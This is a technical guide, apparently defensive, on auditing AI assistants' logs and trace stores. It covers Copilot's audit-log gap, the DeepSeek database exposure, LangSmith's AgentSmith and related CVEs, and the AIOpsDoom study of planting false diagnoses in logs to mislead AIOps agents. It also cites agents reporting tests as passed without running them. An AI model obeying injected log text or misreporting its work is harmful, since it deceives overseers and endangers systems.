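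Esakkiraja, Akhiyarov and colleagues (2026), in *Therefore I am. I Think*, found signs that a decision can come before the reasoning. They used the internal activity of two small models to predict, usually correctly, whether the model would call a tool, before it had written any reasoning. They then altered that activity to push the models towards or away from a tool call. In one case, a user asked for the song "Baby Shark", but the only available tool set the volume. The unaltered model explained that it couldn't play music. The altered model reasoned that it should set the volume to 100, and did so. Its reasoning contained no sign of the researchers' intervention, which had caused the tool call.

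A model's reasoning can still give the tester leads. *Legibility is Not Interpretability (2026)* cites research suggesting that reasoning tends to be faithful when the model needs it to complete a task. If the reasoning mentions an instruction in a shared file, for example, the tester can open that file first.

An agent's final report needs the same caution. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich, 2026) studied 5,115 coding sessions and found that the reports mentioned only about one in eleven of the agent's actions. A short report has to leave things out, but some claims also lacked support. In one session, the agent reported "All tests pass", but according to the log it had searched the test files and never run them.

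Even a recorded tool call may not match what the computer ran, because software between the agent and the operating system can change quotation marks, backslashes or long commands. Yang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?*, examined sessions by six developers on Windows. Claude Code's command-line tool altered 12.0% of calls that contained code, escape sequences or long text. When the change affected backslashes, the wrong action ran with no reported error in 80.7% of cases. A tester who finds a harmful command in a trace should therefore check the system record before reporting that it ran as written.

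## Microsoft 365 Copilot's audit log and the file accesses it missed

Microsoft 365 Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers, where a company can't install AgentSight. To find out which files Copilot opened for an employee, the company has to rely on Microsoft's audit log. Until August 2025, that log could omit a file that Copilot had just summarised.

### The 2025 fault

Zack Korman, chief technology officer of the security training company Pistachio, found the fault on July 4, 2025. He was producing log entries to test a feature his company was developing, and noticed that some were incomplete. Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won't Tell You* gives his account. When someone asked Copilot to summarise a file, the log normally listed that file, but not if the user asked Copilot to leave the link to the file out of the summary.

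Copilot can open only the files that the signed-in user has permission to open, so the fault didn't give anyone access to forbidden documents. But an employee about to join a competitor could have used Copilot to summarise many files without leaving a record of which ones. Korman also points to organisations that must keep strict records of who has read personal data, such as those covered by HIPAA, the US health privacy law.

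Some trace of the conversation probably remained in the log. heise online's *AI assistant* describes an empty log entry, and Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) describes an event without the file's name. An investigator could then have seen when the employee used Copilot, but not what Copilot read.

Korman doesn't give a cause. The pattern suggests that the log's list of files came from the links in the answer, not from the files Copilot had opened.

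It is also unclear how often the fault occurred. Korman says it could happen by chance and concludes that any organisation with Copilot licences probably has an incorrect log, but he doesn't give a rate. He couldn't show an example of a chance omission because Copilot had shortened his chat history.

### Microsoft's response

Korman reported the fault to the Microsoft Security Response Center, which began trying to reproduce it on July 7. On July 10 he noticed that Copilot's behaviour had changed, although nobody had told him about a fix. On August 2, Microsoft told him that it would release a full fix on August 17 and that he could publish his findings on August 18.

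Microsoft may have known about the problem for much longer. Michael Bargury, a co-founder of the security company Zenity, spoke about Copilot at the Black Hat conference in August 2024. Schwartz (2024) reported in *How to Weaponize Microsoft Copilot for Cyberattackers* Bargury's claim that attackers could use Copilot to extract data "without producing logs". Korman learned of the talk after his own discovery and says Bargury had found and disclosed the same fault.

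Microsoft declined to give the fault an identifier in the CVE catalogue. It first told Korman that it issues these identifiers only when customers have to act, and that customers would receive this fix automatically. That contradicted Microsoft's *Toward greater transparency* (2024), which had promised identifiers for critical vulnerabilities in cloud services whether or not customers had to act. When Korman pointed this out, Microsoft replied that it had rated the fault "important", not "critical".

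Korman accepts that the second reason fits Microsoft's policy but objects to the policy itself. Under the CVE programme's rules, which Microsoft quoted in its 2024 announcement, a supplier should publish a vulnerability that could cause significant harm or that requires "action or risk assessment" by others. Korman argues that Microsoft should apply this test to each vulnerability instead of relying on its own severity rating.

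His objection is a good one, because repairing Copilot doesn't restore the file names it failed to record. Customers still had to consider whether they could trust their old logs. For example, a company might have cleared an employee of taking files because the log showed no access to them. On August 14, Microsoft told Korman that it had no plans to inform customers.

After the fix, Office 365 for IT Pros asked Copilot to summarise a document without linking to it or listing it as a reference. The audit record named the files that Copilot had reviewed. This result is independent confirmation of the fix, but it covers only one request in one version of Copilot.

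### What the record contains now

Microsoft creates a record each time someone uses Copilot, provided that the company has auditing switched on. Administrators can search these records in Purview, Microsoft's set of tools for compliance and data protection. The following record is invented and simplified, but the capitalised field names come from Microsoft's documentation. Ana has asked Copilot about parental leave:

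```
user                    ana
time                    09:14
AppHost                 BizChat
AccessedResources
  Name                  Staff handbook.docx
  Action                Read
  Status                success
  SensitivityLabelId    f41a...
  XPIADetected          false
Messages
  message 1             prompt      JailbreakDetected: false
  message 2             response
```

`AppHost` shows where Ana used Copilot, in this case the general chat program. Other values include Word and Outlook. The record can also identify the model that answered and any agent or plugin involved. If Copilot searched the public web, the list of plugins contains the value "BingWebSearch".

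`AccessedResources` should list every file, email or other item that Copilot accessed for the request, and whether Copilot read, created or changed the item. For an item's sensitivity label (the company's own classification, such as "confidential"), the record holds only an identifier, so an assessor has to look up the label's name. If a policy stopped Copilot from using an item, the record can name the policy.

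These entries have the type `CopilotInteraction`. Korman notes that they are separate from the entries logged when a user opens a file in SharePoint, Microsoft's document storage service. He thinks this is right, because the user didn't open the file directly. But an investigator who searches only for ordinary file accesses will miss everything Copilot read.

The record has two flags for attacks. `XPIADetected` is for indirect prompt injection, which Microsoft calls a cross prompt injection attack. Each accessed item can have its own `XPIADetected` flag, so an investigator can see which document contained the suspicious text. That would have been useful in the ServiceNow demonstration, where the malicious instructions were in a ticket. `JailbreakDetected` marks a prompt in which the user may have tried to get around the model's safety rules.

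Both flags depend on a detector that can make mistakes. In a June playbook for investigating Copilot, Microsoft (2026) advises investigators to treat a positive jailbreak flag as a possible attack, not a confirmed one, according to TechInformed. A negative flag is also weak evidence, because the detector may have missed an attack.

The playbook recommends first finding out who used Copilot, when and in which service, and then which items it accessed, before judging the alerts. This order is sensible because the same alert could come from an attacker or from an employee running an approved test. Investigators are also supposed to use the list of accessed items to work out how much data an incident affected, which they will underestimate if the list is incomplete.

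### Where Microsoft keeps the prompts and answers

The audit log doesn't contain the text of prompts or answers. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* compares this with email, where the log also leaves out the subject and body. Many administrators can read the log, so if it included the text, an attacker who took over one of their accounts could collect confidential text from it.

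Microsoft stores most of the text in a hidden folder in the user's mailbox, according to Microsoft's *Apply retention policies to Copilot prompts and responses*. Text from Copilot in Teams, Microsoft's chat and meeting program, stays in the Teams chat service. An assessor can reach the text in several ways, each with its own conditions:

| Record | What it contains | What the assessor needs |
|---|---|---|
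| Audit log | User, time, application, accessed items, labels and flags | Auditing switched on and permission to search the log |
| Purview's activity explorer | Prompts and answers | A role that allows the holder to view content |
| eDiscovery, Purview's search tool for legal cases | Prompts and answers | Special privileges and a search aimed at Copilot conversations |
| Export interface for programs | Prompts and answers, with an identifier linking each pair | A Copilot licence and a permission approved by an administrator |

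Microsoft lists two suitable roles for the activity explorer, Content Explorer Content Viewer and Purview Data Security AI Content Viewer. The export interface doesn't cover every application. Microsoft lists filters for Word, Excel, Teams and Copilot's chat programs, but not for PowerPoint or Outlook, so an assessor who relies on the export could wrongly conclude that nobody had used Copilot to write emails.

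The text of a conversation may also no longer exist. Companies set retention policies that keep or delete it, and a policy covers most Copilot conversations only if the company selects "Microsoft Copilot experiences" as a location. Microsoft didn't add this location to existing policies automatically. Even companies that selected it may have gaps, because Microsoft's *Data Lifecycle Management* (2026) says retention had not consistently covered all Copilot applications. Microsoft began extending retention to all supported applications on June 17, 2026.

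Where the conversation text survives, it can help with incidents from before the August 2025 fix. An investigator could search the stored answers for names or figures from a sensitive file, even if the audit log never listed that file. Some of the text may need decoding first. When Office 365 for IT Pros examined the raw mailbox records, part of each conversation was encoded in Base64, which is easy to decode but which an ordinary text search won't match.

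### What an assessor can establish, and what stays hidden

With a complete set of records, an assessor can show when Ana used Copilot, in which application, and which files it accessed for her. The assessor can then compare those files with her permissions at that time, as in the test with two identities. In the confidential-email fault, customers could have searched the records for the "confidential" label, provided that Copilot logged the emails correctly.

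The record doesn't show how Copilot selected the files. Suppose its search for Ana's question also returned Tomas's medical file, which Copilot discarded before writing the answer. Microsoft doesn't document whether such a file counts as accessed. If the file appears in Ana's record, the assessor has something to investigate, but the search may have returned it even if it doesn't appear there.

The documented fields also omit the search query, the passages Copilot took from each file, and the prompts it sent to the model between steps. An assessor therefore can't tell whether the model read a whole document or one paragraph, or whether an instruction in that document changed what Copilot did next.

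The record also shows little about permission checks. It can include the policy that blocked an item, but when Copilot reads a file successfully, no documented field shows which check allowed it. If Ana was entitled to the file, an assessor can't tell whether her permission was checked correctly or not checked at all.

The user's identity may also be missing from the log. Companies can build their own agents with Microsoft's tools, and some of these agents don't require users to log in. TechInformed notes that this can make it hard to connect an agent's activity to a named person.

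### Gaps found before and after the fix

Copilot's audit log had also been incomplete before Korman's discovery. Until March 2024, the list of accessed items was empty when Copilot answered questions about a meeting, even though Copilot used the meeting's transcript. Microsoft's *AccessedResources field populated in Purview for Meeting Copilot Interactions* announced that the list would begin to include a link to the recording.

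A more serious gap came to light in late August 2025, less than two weeks after Microsoft's fix for Korman's fault. The security company Datadog was studying Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents. Datadog's *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) lists four kinds of administrative change that the log should have recorded but didn't:

- changing how users log in to an agent
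- changing the settings for the agent's separate log of conversations
- sharing the agent with other users
- publishing a new version

Together, these gaps could have hidden a whole attack. Someone with permission to edit an agent could have removed its login requirement, switched off its conversation log and published the new version. They could then have questioned the agent anonymously from outside the company. The anonymous conversation wouldn't have created a Copilot record either, because those records require a logged-in user. Datadog describes this as a possible attack but doesn't report that anyone carried it out.

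Microsoft rated this fault "important" too and repaired it by October 5. Datadog confirmed that all four events were appearing, but in November the two for changes to login and conversation logging were missing again. By January 2026 one of the two appeared some of the time. In March, Microsoft said its engineers could not reproduce the problem, while Datadog said it was still occurring. Datadog has a commercial interest because it sells software that looks for these events, but it published its method and a detailed timeline that others can check.

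From late October 2025, according to Microsoft (2025), the log also began to include changes that administrators make to Copilot agents in the Microsoft 365 admin centre. Log entries from September 2025 therefore can't show whether anyone made such changes that month.

Assessors need to test for themselves whether a particular log is complete, because documentation can't establish this. When Korman found the fault in July 2025, Microsoft's documentation already described the list of accessed items as covering all resources.

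### A test that compares known accesses with the log

In a log-reconciliation test, a tester performs a known set of actions and checks that each one appears in the log. The following example is invented, but its waiting period comes from Datadog, whose researchers checked the log after 30 minutes and again after 24 hours before concluding that events were missing.

The tester creates a test account and 60 files, each with a different code word in its text but not in its title. If Copilot's answer contains the code word, Copilot must have read the file. Each request needs a different file and a new conversation, because Copilot might otherwise repeat a code word from an earlier answer without opening the file again.

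Before starting, the tester writes down each planned request, the file it concerns and the record that should result. The requests should vary in the ways that staff requests do. In this example, a third concern a document open in Word, a third ask Copilot Chat for a summary with a link, and a third ask for a summary without one. After 24 hours, the tester exports the log and matches its entries with the list by user, time and file:

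| Type of request | Requests | Answers with the code word | Of these, file named in the log |
|---|---|---|---|
| Document open in Word | 20 | 20 | 20 |
| Copilot Chat, with a link | 20 | 20 | 20 |
| Copilot Chat, without a link | 20 | 19 | 16 |
| Total | 60 | 59 | 56 |

The log missed 3 of 59 known accesses, or about 5%. But all three were among the 19 accesses in the last group, a miss rate of about 16%. The tester should report the groups separately, because the overall rate depends on how many requests of each type the tester chose. The 20 correct results in each of the other groups are compatible with a failure rate of up to 13.9%, as with 20 clean replays.

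Copilot's answer to one request didn't contain the code word. Copilot may have failed to find the file, or may have read it and left the word out, so the tester can't count the request as a known access, whatever the log shows.

Two further checks make the results easier to interpret. The tester can ask questions that don't require any file, to see whether the log lists files Copilot had no reason to open. As with traces, the tester can also ask about a forbidden file to see whether the log records the refusal.

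A similar test can cover administrative changes. The tester builds a harmless agent, then changes its login settings, switches its conversation log off and on, shares it and publishes it. The tester needs to repeat each change several times, because Datadog found that the same action did not always create a record.

Many companies copy the audit log into a separate security monitoring system, and records can go missing on the way. Graslie (2026), in *What Your M365 Logs Are Not Telling You*, warns that Copilot's records silently stop arriving if the company isn't subscribed to the feed called Audit.General. The commonly used OfficeActivity table holds only about 40% of the activity in Microsoft's log by default. The tester should therefore look for the same 56 records in the monitoring system. If records are in Purview but not in the monitoring system, the company can probably fix the problem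 by changing its settings, but only Microsoft can fix the 3 that are missing from Purview.

The company should repeat the test regularly, because Microsoft can change Copilot at any time without the customer installing anything. Korman saw Copilot's behaviour change before anyone told him about a fix, and two of Datadog's events disappeared again after a successful retest.

### Assistants from other companies

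Purview can also record the use of AI applications that Microsoft doesn't make. Some are applications the customer has deployed and registered, and others are outside services its employees visit, which Purview monitors through the browser or the network. According to Microsoft's documentation, the customer has to switch on this logging and pay for each record, and Microsoft keeps the records for 180 days.

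These records come from outside the AI application, so they can serve as a check on the vendor's own log, but they show less of what happened. For applications that the company doesn't manage, the activity explorer includes only the text prompts from Microsoft's Edge browser, not the answers, according to Microsoft. A browser also can't record which files an assistant opens on its vendor's servers after it receives the prompt.

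An assessor of ChatGPT Enterprise, Claude Enterprise or Gemini in Google Workspace therefore needs the vendor's log as well. Before the test with code words, the assessor should find out whether that log includes conversation text, whether it lists tool calls and opened files, how long the vendor keeps it and how to export it. The test can then show whether the log contains what the vendor promises in its documentation.

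## LangSmith and DeepSeek: when tracing platforms and log stores are exposed

Recording full prompts, keeping every trace and saving tool results for replay gives testers better evidence, but it also creates a store that an attacker would want to read. In January 2025, researchers found that anyone on the internet could access a log database belonging to the AI company DeepSeek. Five months later, other researchers disclosed a flaw in the tracing platform LangSmith that could send a user's prompts and keys to an attacker, even if the attacker never opened a stored trace.

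### What an attacker can find in a trace store

If content capture had been on when Ana asked about parental leave, the trace could contain her question, her leave balance and a paragraph from Tomas's medical file. Anyone who debugs the assistant might be able to read that paragraph without permission to open the file, and so could an attacker who took over one developer's account. If the company later deleted the file or restricted it further, the copy in the trace would not change.

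Traces can also contain credentials such as API keys, the secret strings that programs send to services to identify themselves. Developers sometimes pass a key as a tool argument or print one in an error message. An attacker who finds a working key can use the service that accepts it, as well as read old records.

Miggo Security, which found a separate flaw in LangSmith, says the platform handles nearly a billion events a day. Traces often keep the raw details that developers need for debugging, so an intruder could find internal database queries, customer records or source code in the tool calls.

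### DeepSeek's open database

The security company Wiz found roughly 30 public web addresses belonging to DeepSeek. Most looked harmless, but two led to a ClickHouse database that required no password. Companies often use ClickHouse to store and search logs. Wiz announced the discovery on January 29, 2025, and Fortune (2025) reported it two days later.

One table, called `log_stream`, held more than a million entries. Wiz picked out these fields:

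| Field | Contents, according to Wiz |
|---|---|
| `timestamp` | Times of the entries, starting on January 6, 2025 |
| `span_name` | References to DeepSeek's internal services |
| `string.values` | Plain text, including chat history, API keys and technical details |
| `_service` | The service that produced the entry |
| `_source` | Where the request came from, along with chat history, API keys and folder structures |

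We can't infer the number of users or conversations from the number of entries, because one chat message can produce many entries and some may contain no chat text. The `span_name` field suggests that at least some records came from tracing software, but Wiz calls them logs and doesn't say whether they had the identifiers needed to join them into traces.

The database accepted any command, so an intruder could have changed or deleted entries as well as read them. Depending on the database's configuration, the intruder might also have been able to read other files on the server. Wiz didn't try this, because it limited itself to finding out what the database contained.

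The immediate cause was a database that anyone could reach without logging in. Wiz doesn't explain why DeepSeek left it open, but says the company closed it promptly after Wiz reported it.

Wiz doesn't say whether anyone else had found the database. Its researchers found it within minutes, so others could have too. The earliest timestamp doesn't show when the exposure began, since DeepSeek might have exposed the database later or deleted older entries. DeepSeek could look for other visitors in its network and database access records, but an intruder with full control of the database might have been able to delete some of those records.

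### AgentSmith: a shared agent with a hidden destination

LangSmith includes a public library, the Prompt Hub, where users share prompts and agents. Noma Security found that a shared agent could secretly send its users' data to an attacker, and called the flaw AgentSmith. According to The Hacker News, the flaw scored 8.8 out of 10 on CVSS, a standard scale of vulnerability severity.

The flaw came from a feature that let an agent's creator choose which model server the agent contacted. The choice stayed in place when other people used the agent, so an attacker could publish an agent that sent everything through a proxy server they controlled. The proxy would receive the user's prompts, uploaded files and OpenAI API key. It could also change the model's answers, as Hackread's *AgentSmith Flaw in LangSmith's Prompt Hub Exposed User API Keys, Data* explains. If someone copied the agent into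 their company's account, the proxy setting went with it, and the company could keep leaking data without noticing.

Noma reported the flaw on October 29, 2024, and LangChain, which makes LangSmith, deployed a fix on November 6. LangSmith now warns users who try to copy an agent with a custom proxy and displays a permanent banner on the agent's page. Users still have to judge whether a proxy is safe.

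Neither company found evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw, according to Hackread. In a statement quoted by BeyondMachines, LangChain said the flaw affected only public sharing in the Prompt Hub and people who chose to use a malicious prompt. Anyone who used one would have needed to replace their keys, as a security specialist advised in Security Magazine, because fixing LangSmith doesn't cancel a stolen key.

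DeepSeek's database exposed stored records of people who had done nothing unusual, while AgentSmith exposed data in transit, and only for people who ran a malicious agent. Checking who had opened LangSmith's traces would not have revealed AgentSmith, because the attacker didn't need to open any. The model server's address, recorded either on the span for each model call or in a log of outgoing connections, would be better evidence.

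### CVE-2026-45134: the same idea in a code library

In May 2026, a similar flaw became known in LangSmith's software development kit (SDK), the code library that developers add to their applications. Applications can use the SDK to download prompts from the Prompt Hub. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2582* (2026), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities, explains that a downloaded prompt can also contain settings, including the address of a model server. The SDK loaded these settings in the same way whether the prompt came from the company itself or from a stranger.

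An application was at risk if it fetched a public prompt that an untrusted or compromised account had published or changed, and its developers used the prompt without checking it. The attacker could receive the application's prompts, retrieved chunks and its key for the model provider. An application in daily use could send text from real staff files, whereas a person trying out an agent in AgentSmith might send only a test question. GitLab's *CVE-2026-45134* (2026) gives the flaw a CVSS score of 7.1.

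The SDK no longer fetches another organisation's public prompts unless the developer sets an option whose name begins with "dangerously". This is stronger than a warning banner because developers must change their code to accept the risk. The fix is in version 0.8.0 for Python and 0.6.0 for JavaScript.

The new option doesn't cover prompts from the company's own account, so an attacker who steals a LangSmith key that can change prompts can still redirect the application's model traffic. OSV therefore advises companies to review changes to prompts as carefully as changes to code. The advisory doesn't mention any known attacks.

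### Flaws that expose traces

An attacker can access a trace while the application is sending it to the store (ingestion) or when people or programs read it (viewing). LangSmith had flaws at both stages.

LangSmith's SDK could read settings from baggage, the same web header that the Kubernetes proposal would use to carry user identities. According to OSV's *GHSA-v34v-rq6j-cj6p* (2026), older versions let any caller use these settings to add another address to send the trace to. Someone who sent a request could therefore receive its complete trace, including the model's inputs and outputs. The flaw affected only applications that read this header from untrusted callers.

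OSV lists the severity as moderate, but the harm depends on what the traces contain. In the test with two identities, seven of Ana's questions retrieved forbidden text but got harmless answers. If the staff assistant had this flaw and recorded document text, Ana could have read the forbidden text in the traces even though the answers did not reveal it.

Another ingestion flaw caused LangSmith to store text that developers had chosen to hide. LangSmith's SDK has a setting that keeps model outputs out of traces. But when an application streamed an answer in pieces, the SDK recorded each piece as a separate event and did not apply the setting to those events, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-41182* (2026). A tester who checked only the output field could have concluded that the setting worked.

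The flaw was in LangSmith Studio, the part of the platform where developers run and inspect agents. If a logged-in user visited a malicious website, their browser could send the attacker a token that gave access to the account. Miggo says the attacker would have had five minutes to use the token to read traces, change settings or delete projects. Miggo reported the flaw on December 1, 2025, and gives both December 15 and December 20 as the date LangChain fixed the cloud service. On January 7, 2026, LangChain said it had found no evidence of exploitation.

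Red Hat's *CVE-2026-8147* describes a simpler flaw in MLflow, which let any logged-in user read, change or delete traces from experiments they had no permission to open. MLflow had permission checks for experiments but didn't apply them to requests for traces (Red Hat, 2026). An employee who had misused an AI assistant could have deleted the evidence, or changed it to implicate someone else. An assessor who relies on traces from an affected MLflow server should therefore look for a second record of the same events.

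### Flaws in other functions of the same platforms

Tracing platforms do much more than store traces, so a vulnerability in one doesn't necessarily expose traces. Langfuse, for example, stores the API keys that let its users call models from the platform. OSV's *CVE-2026-41487* (2026) describes a flaw that let an ordinary project member obtain such a key in plain text. The flaw didn't give the member access to any new traces, but they could have used the key outside Langfuse, where the platform's limits on members don't apply.

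Langfuse can also announce changes to a company's prompts in Slack, a workplace chat service. Akaoma's *CVE-2026-24055 Vulnerability Analysis & Exploit Details* reports that an outsider could connect their own Slack workspace to another company's project and potentially receive these announcements. The outsider might have learned the assistant's instructions this way, but not what its users had asked.

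An earlier Langfuse flaw from November 2025 let users of one organisation list the names and email addresses of another's members if they knew that organisation's identifier. vuln.today's *CVE-2025-64504* (2025) quotes a statement that no traces, prompts or evaluations were accessible. Separation between customers can therefore fail in one part of a platform and work in another, so a tester has to check it separately for traces.

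Two MLflow flaws are harder to classify because they are outside the tracing function but may still expose traces. Vulners' *CVE-2026-2614 Arbitrary File Read via Prompt Tag Source Validation Bypass in mlflow/mlflow* describes one that let an outsider read any file on the server by misusing a tag meant for prompts. Zero Day Initiative's *MLflow Tracking Server Artifact Handler Directory Traversal Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2026) describes another, in the code that handles stored files, that let an outsider run code on the server without logging in. An attacker using either flaw could probably reach the traces if the server keeps them on the same machine or holds the password to the database that contains them.

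| Route | Flaw | What an attacker could get | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ingestion | LangSmith SDK, CVE-2026-25528 | Complete traces of the attacker's requests | Python 0.6.3, JavaScript 0.4.6 |
| Ingestion | LangSmith SDK, CVE-2026-41182 | Model outputs that should have been hidden, if the attacker can read the traces | Python 0.7.31, JavaScript 0.5.19 |
| Viewing | LangSmith Studio, CVE-2026-25750 | A user's account, including its traces | Self-hosted 0.12.71; LangChain repaired the cloud service |
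| Viewing | MLflow, CVE-2026-8147 | Other experiments' traces, and the ability to change or delete them | 3.14.0 |
| Sharing | LangSmith Prompt Hub, AgentSmith | Prompts, files and keys in transit | LangChain added warnings |
| Prompt management | LangSmith SDK, CVE-2026-45134 | Model traffic and keys in transit | Python 0.8.0, JavaScript 0.6.0 |
| Prompt management | Langfuse, CVE-2026-24055 | Announcements of prompt changes | 3.147.0 |
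| Prompt management | MLflow, CVE-2026-2614 | Files on the server, possibly including traces | A version after 3.9.0 |
| Storage | Langfuse, CVE-2026-41487 | Model providers' keys | 3.167.0 |
| Storage | MLflow file handling | Control of the MLflow service, possibly including traces | An MLflow update |

Phoenix's absence from the table doesn't show that it is safer. According to a reply on Arize's community forum, no published list of vulnerabilities was found for the latest version. Searches by name can also return results for an unrelated web framework called Phoenix.

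When LangChain repaired LangSmith's cloud service, every cloud customer was protected at once, but flaws in the SDK remain in each customer's applications until someone updates the SDK there. An assessor should therefore ask for the SDK version in every application as well as the platform version. Python version 0.8.0 and JavaScript version 0.6.0 contain all the fixes for the three LangSmith SDK flaws above.

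### How text in a trace can mislead an AI system

An attacker who can't read a trace store may still be able to write to it, because applications record text that outsiders send them, such as a web address, a username or the name of the visitor's browser. *Agentic Cloud Decoys* (2026), a study of AI systems that investigate intrusions, argues that a log is therefore untrusted input whenever a language model reads it. An attacker who plants instructions in the log is using indirect prompt injection, as in the payroll example, but with a log instead of a shared file.

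In *When AIOps Become “AI Oops”*, Pasquini, Kornaropoulos and colleagues tested this attack on AIOps (AI for IT operations) agents, which diagnose faults in computer systems. They released the study in August 2025, and the USENIX Security conference accepted it for 2026.

The tool AIOpsDoom sends requests that are likely to cause errors in a system. Each request contains a false explanation of the error and a harmful "repair", such as installing an older program version with a known security flaw. The system records this text along with the error. When the errors set off an alert, an agent reads the records to find the cause and may recommend the attacker's repair or carry it out. The attacker needs no account and no knowledge of the agent.

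The researchers used three test applications, two kinds of agent, two models and three harmful repairs. They ran each of the 36 combinations five times, for 180 trials:

| Trials | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| All 180 | 90% |
| Agents using GPT-4o | 96% |
| Agents using GPT-4.1 | 84% |
| The more advanced agent, Flash, with GPT-4.1 | 82.2% |
| Hotel booking application, where the attacker's text reached only traces | 82% |

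An attack counted as successful if the agent proposed the attacker's repair. A language model judged this, and the researchers found no mistakes when they checked 20 cases by hand. Their breakdown of failed attacks lists 20 failures, which would give a success rate of 88.9%, so the 90% figure is slightly uncertain.

The hotel application's result is the most important one for tracing, because most attacks worked even though the traces recorded only the web addresses of outsiders' requests. These addresses distorted the planted text by replacing spaces and punctuation with codes. Turning off content capture therefore doesn't remove the danger if the trace still includes addresses, usernames or error messages from outside.

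In a separate test, ordinary prompt injections, which try to override the agent's task, failed every time. In about half of those runs, the agent recognised an attack and suggested ways to stop it. A false diagnosis is harder to recognise because it seems to help with the task. The agent sometimes made the diagnosis more convincing by adding true details, such as the exact version of the server. Those details could also mislead a person reviewing the recommendation.

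The 90% success rate probably overstates the danger in everyday use. The applications had no real faults, so the models had no true explanation to choose over the planted one. Both models are also well over a year old, and the newer one resisted more attacks. But even a much lower success rate could be serious for an agent that carries out repairs without approval.

Pasquini and colleagues also built a defence, AIOpsShield. Before the agent starts work, AIOpsShield sends a code word through the application to find which recorded fields outsiders can fill. It then replaces the contents of those fields with labels such as "User#12" before the agent reads them. None of the original attacks succeeded against it. The defence could fail if this initial setup misses a field, and it doesn't protect other sources the agent reads.

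AIOpsShield would be less useful for investigating an AI assistant, because it would hide the user's question and the retrieved chunks, which a tester needs to read to find an indirect prompt injection. It leaves the original records unchanged, so a team could give the shortened version to an AI analyser and let people read the full text. If the analyser needs the full text too, it shouldn't be able to change any systems, and a person should check its conclusions against the underlying spans, as with AgentSight's second model.

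### A checklist for assessing a trace store

The assessor should use test accounts, invented data and a separate test project. These checks cover the main weaknesses in the cases above:

| Check | Test | Result that needs a repair |
|---|---|---|
| Tenant separation | Use an account from one project to read, change and delete another project's test trace | Any of these attempts succeeds |
| Key scope | Take the key that an application uses to send traces and try to read traces or change prompts with it | The key does more than the application needs |
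| Secret removal | Put a fake API key in a prompt, a document, a tool result, an error message and a streamed answer, then export the trace | The key appears anywhere in the export |
| Safe display | Record harmless web code that would load an image from a test server, then open the trace | The test server receives a request |
| AI analysis | Put a false but harmless explanation in an error message and ask the analyser for the cause | The analyser accepts the explanation without other evidence |
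| Export | List every destination for traces and compare the list with the application's outgoing connections | Traces go somewhere that isn't on the list |
| Deletion | Delete a trace that contains a code word, then search every place that held a copy | The code word remains after the promised deletion time |

To test tenant separation, the assessor should send requests directly to the platform's API as well as using its web pages, because a page may hide another project's traces while the server still returns them to anyone who requests them by identifier. The assessor should also send requests without logging in, which would have found a database like DeepSeek's.

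The key-scope test should also cover keys that the platform stores for its users. In Langfuse, a project member who wasn't supposed to see the model provider's key could make the platform send it to another address. An assessor can ask who may change the address for each stored connection, and whether changing it requires entering the key again.

The export test should include requests both from staff and from outside the company, because an application may treat their headers differently. It should also cover every shared prompt or agent the team has copied, because AgentSmith sent data out through the model connection and wouldn't have appeared in a list of export settings.

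Deletion is hard to check because one trace can have many copies. The text may be in the trace store, a separate content store, a backup, a test set built from old traces, or a replay recording. The assessor should search for the code word in each of these places and find out when any backups expire. The team also needs a way to pause deletion during an investigation and a record of who deleted what, kept outside the trace store.

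## Privacy and access: what assessors may read

If a company never records the text of Tomas's medical file in its trace store, a leak of that store won't expose it. But then an assessor can't use the trace to show that the assistant put the file into Ana's prompt. Companies have to weigh privacy against evidence both when they decide what to record and when they decide what an outside assessor may read.

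### What each way of recording content lets an assessor prove

Under OpenTelemetry's conventions, a team can leave out the text of prompts and answers, record it on the spans, or store it separately and put a reference on the span. For Ana's question about parental leave, the choice has these effects:

| What the assessor wants to show | No content | Content on the spans | Content in a separate store |
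|---|---|---|---|
| The assistant searched documents and looked up leave | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tomas's passage was in the prompt | No | Yes, unless software shortened or changed the text | Yes, if the text still exists and the assessor may open it |
| The model's answer left Tomas out | No | Yes, with the same exception | Yes, on the same conditions |

With a separate store, a developer investigating a slow search can open the spans without reading about Tomas's health, and the company can log each time someone reads the text. But the reference may outlast the text. If the company deletes text after 30 days and spans after a year, an assessor who arrives in the third month can show that a prompt existed, but not what it said.

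The list of retrieved documents and the tool's arguments have their own opt-in settings, so a team can record document identifiers without recording any of the text. In the test with two identities, the document identifiers, the user and the time were enough to find every question that had retrieved a forbidden document. Document identifiers are therefore among the most useful things to keep for a company that wants to record very little.

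### Removing personal data without losing the evidence

A team that does record content can remove the personal data from it. In this invented example, Ana asks for her own leave balance and a bug makes the assistant look up Tomas's. The trace holds both employee numbers, and the team could hide them in four ways:

```
                  signed-in employee    employee looked up
original          40233                 40718
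deletion          [removed]             [removed]
masking           40***                 40***
pseudonyms        PERSON_1              PERSON_2
keyed hashes      7be2...               c90f...
```

Deleting or masking the two numbers hides the fault, because an assessor can no longer tell that they differ. With consistent pseudonyms, the assessor can still see the difference and report that the assistant looked up PERSON_2 for PERSON_1, without learning who either of them is. The company has to keep a table that links pseudonyms to people, protect it as carefully as the original data, and share it among all the services that write spans.

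Keyed hashes don't need a table. A hash function turns any value into a code of fixed length, and the same value always gives the same code. Running the calculation backwards is impractical, but a plain hash of an employee number is easy to reverse by guessing. A five-digit number has only 100,000 possible values, and an ordinary laptop can hash them all in under a second and look for the matching code.

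A keyed hash, such as HMAC, includes a secret key in the calculation, so people without the key can't test their guesses. The assessor can still see that 7be2 and c90f are different. To find out whether the second code belongs to Tomas, the assessor can ask the company to calculate the code for his number and compare the two. The company should keep the key to itself, since an assessor who had it could try all 100,000 numbers.

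Matching codes are good evidence that the values match, but different codes can stand for the same value. If one service writes an employee number as 40718 and another writes it as 040718, the employee gets two codes. The employee also gets a new code when the company changes the key. Changing the key every month helps privacy by making it harder to follow one person through a year of traces, but it also prevents an assessor from following a fault from one month to the next.

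Personal data in ordinary sentences is harder to deal with, because software first has to find it. A team can measure how well its software does this by planting invented details in prompts, documents and tool results. Suppose it plants 500 and the software removes 480, or 96%. If a long trace contains 20 such details and the misses are independent, the chance that the software removes them all is:

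```
0.96^20 = 0.442, or about 44%
```

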